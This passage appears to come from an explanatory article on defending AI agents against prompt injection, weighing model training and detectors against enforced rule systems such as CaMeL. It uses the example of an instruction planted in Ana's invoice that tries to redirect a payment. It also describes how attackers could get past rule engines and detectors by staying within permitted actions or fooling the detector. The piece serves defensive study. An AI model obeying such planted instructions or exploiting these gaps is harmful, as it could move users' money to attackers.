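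The researchers build security tools based on enforced rules, so they have an interest in the outcome, though they are open about the test's limits. They tried only one attack template and no attack that uses only permitted actions. That omission matters because persuasive text can't change a fixed rule's result, so an attacker who knows the rule will look for harm that it allows, a mistake in a label, or a person who will approve the call. Foerster and colleagues showed that such gaps exist by steering a computer-use agent down branches already in its plan.

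### Using both approaches together

A harmful action requires two things to go wrong, because the model has to propose it and the rules have to allow it:

P(harm) = P(proposed) × P(allowed | proposed).

Training, prompts and detectors reduce the first factor, while enforced rules reduce the second. If Ana's bank tool accepts only accounts on file, the second factor is zero for a payment to the thief's account, whatever the model does. For a payment to the wrong supplier among those on file, the second factor may be 1, and the model's judgement is the main protection left.

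A company can't estimate its risk by multiplying a model's published attack success rate by the share of attacks that a rule engine lets through. Suppose a model proposes the attacker's action in 10% of attacks, and the rules allow 5% of those actions. The product, 0.5%, is the risk only for that mix of attacks. An attacker who knows the rules can stick to actions they allow, which raises the 5% to 100% and the risk to 10%.

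A model that resists planted instructions also makes the rules less disruptive. If it ignores the planted line in Ana's invoice, it doesn't attempt a forbidden payment, and Ana doesn't receive a confusing request for approval. In a system such as CaMeL, the quarantined model still has to extract the right amount and account number. Better training makes those values more reliable, but the labels still mark them as untrusted.

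Detectors can also help. Nasr and colleagues consider them useful for blocking unsophisticated attacks, though determined attackers get past them. In Deep and colleagues' tests, a combination of several black-box defences, without the filter on answers, allowed leaks in only 23 of 5,000 attacks, and none of those leaks contained a complete secret. In Ana's assistant, ordinary code could respond to a detector's warning by asking for approval of a payment that it would otherwise allow. A clean result should never make the code skip a check, because an attacker could then remove the check by fooling the detector.
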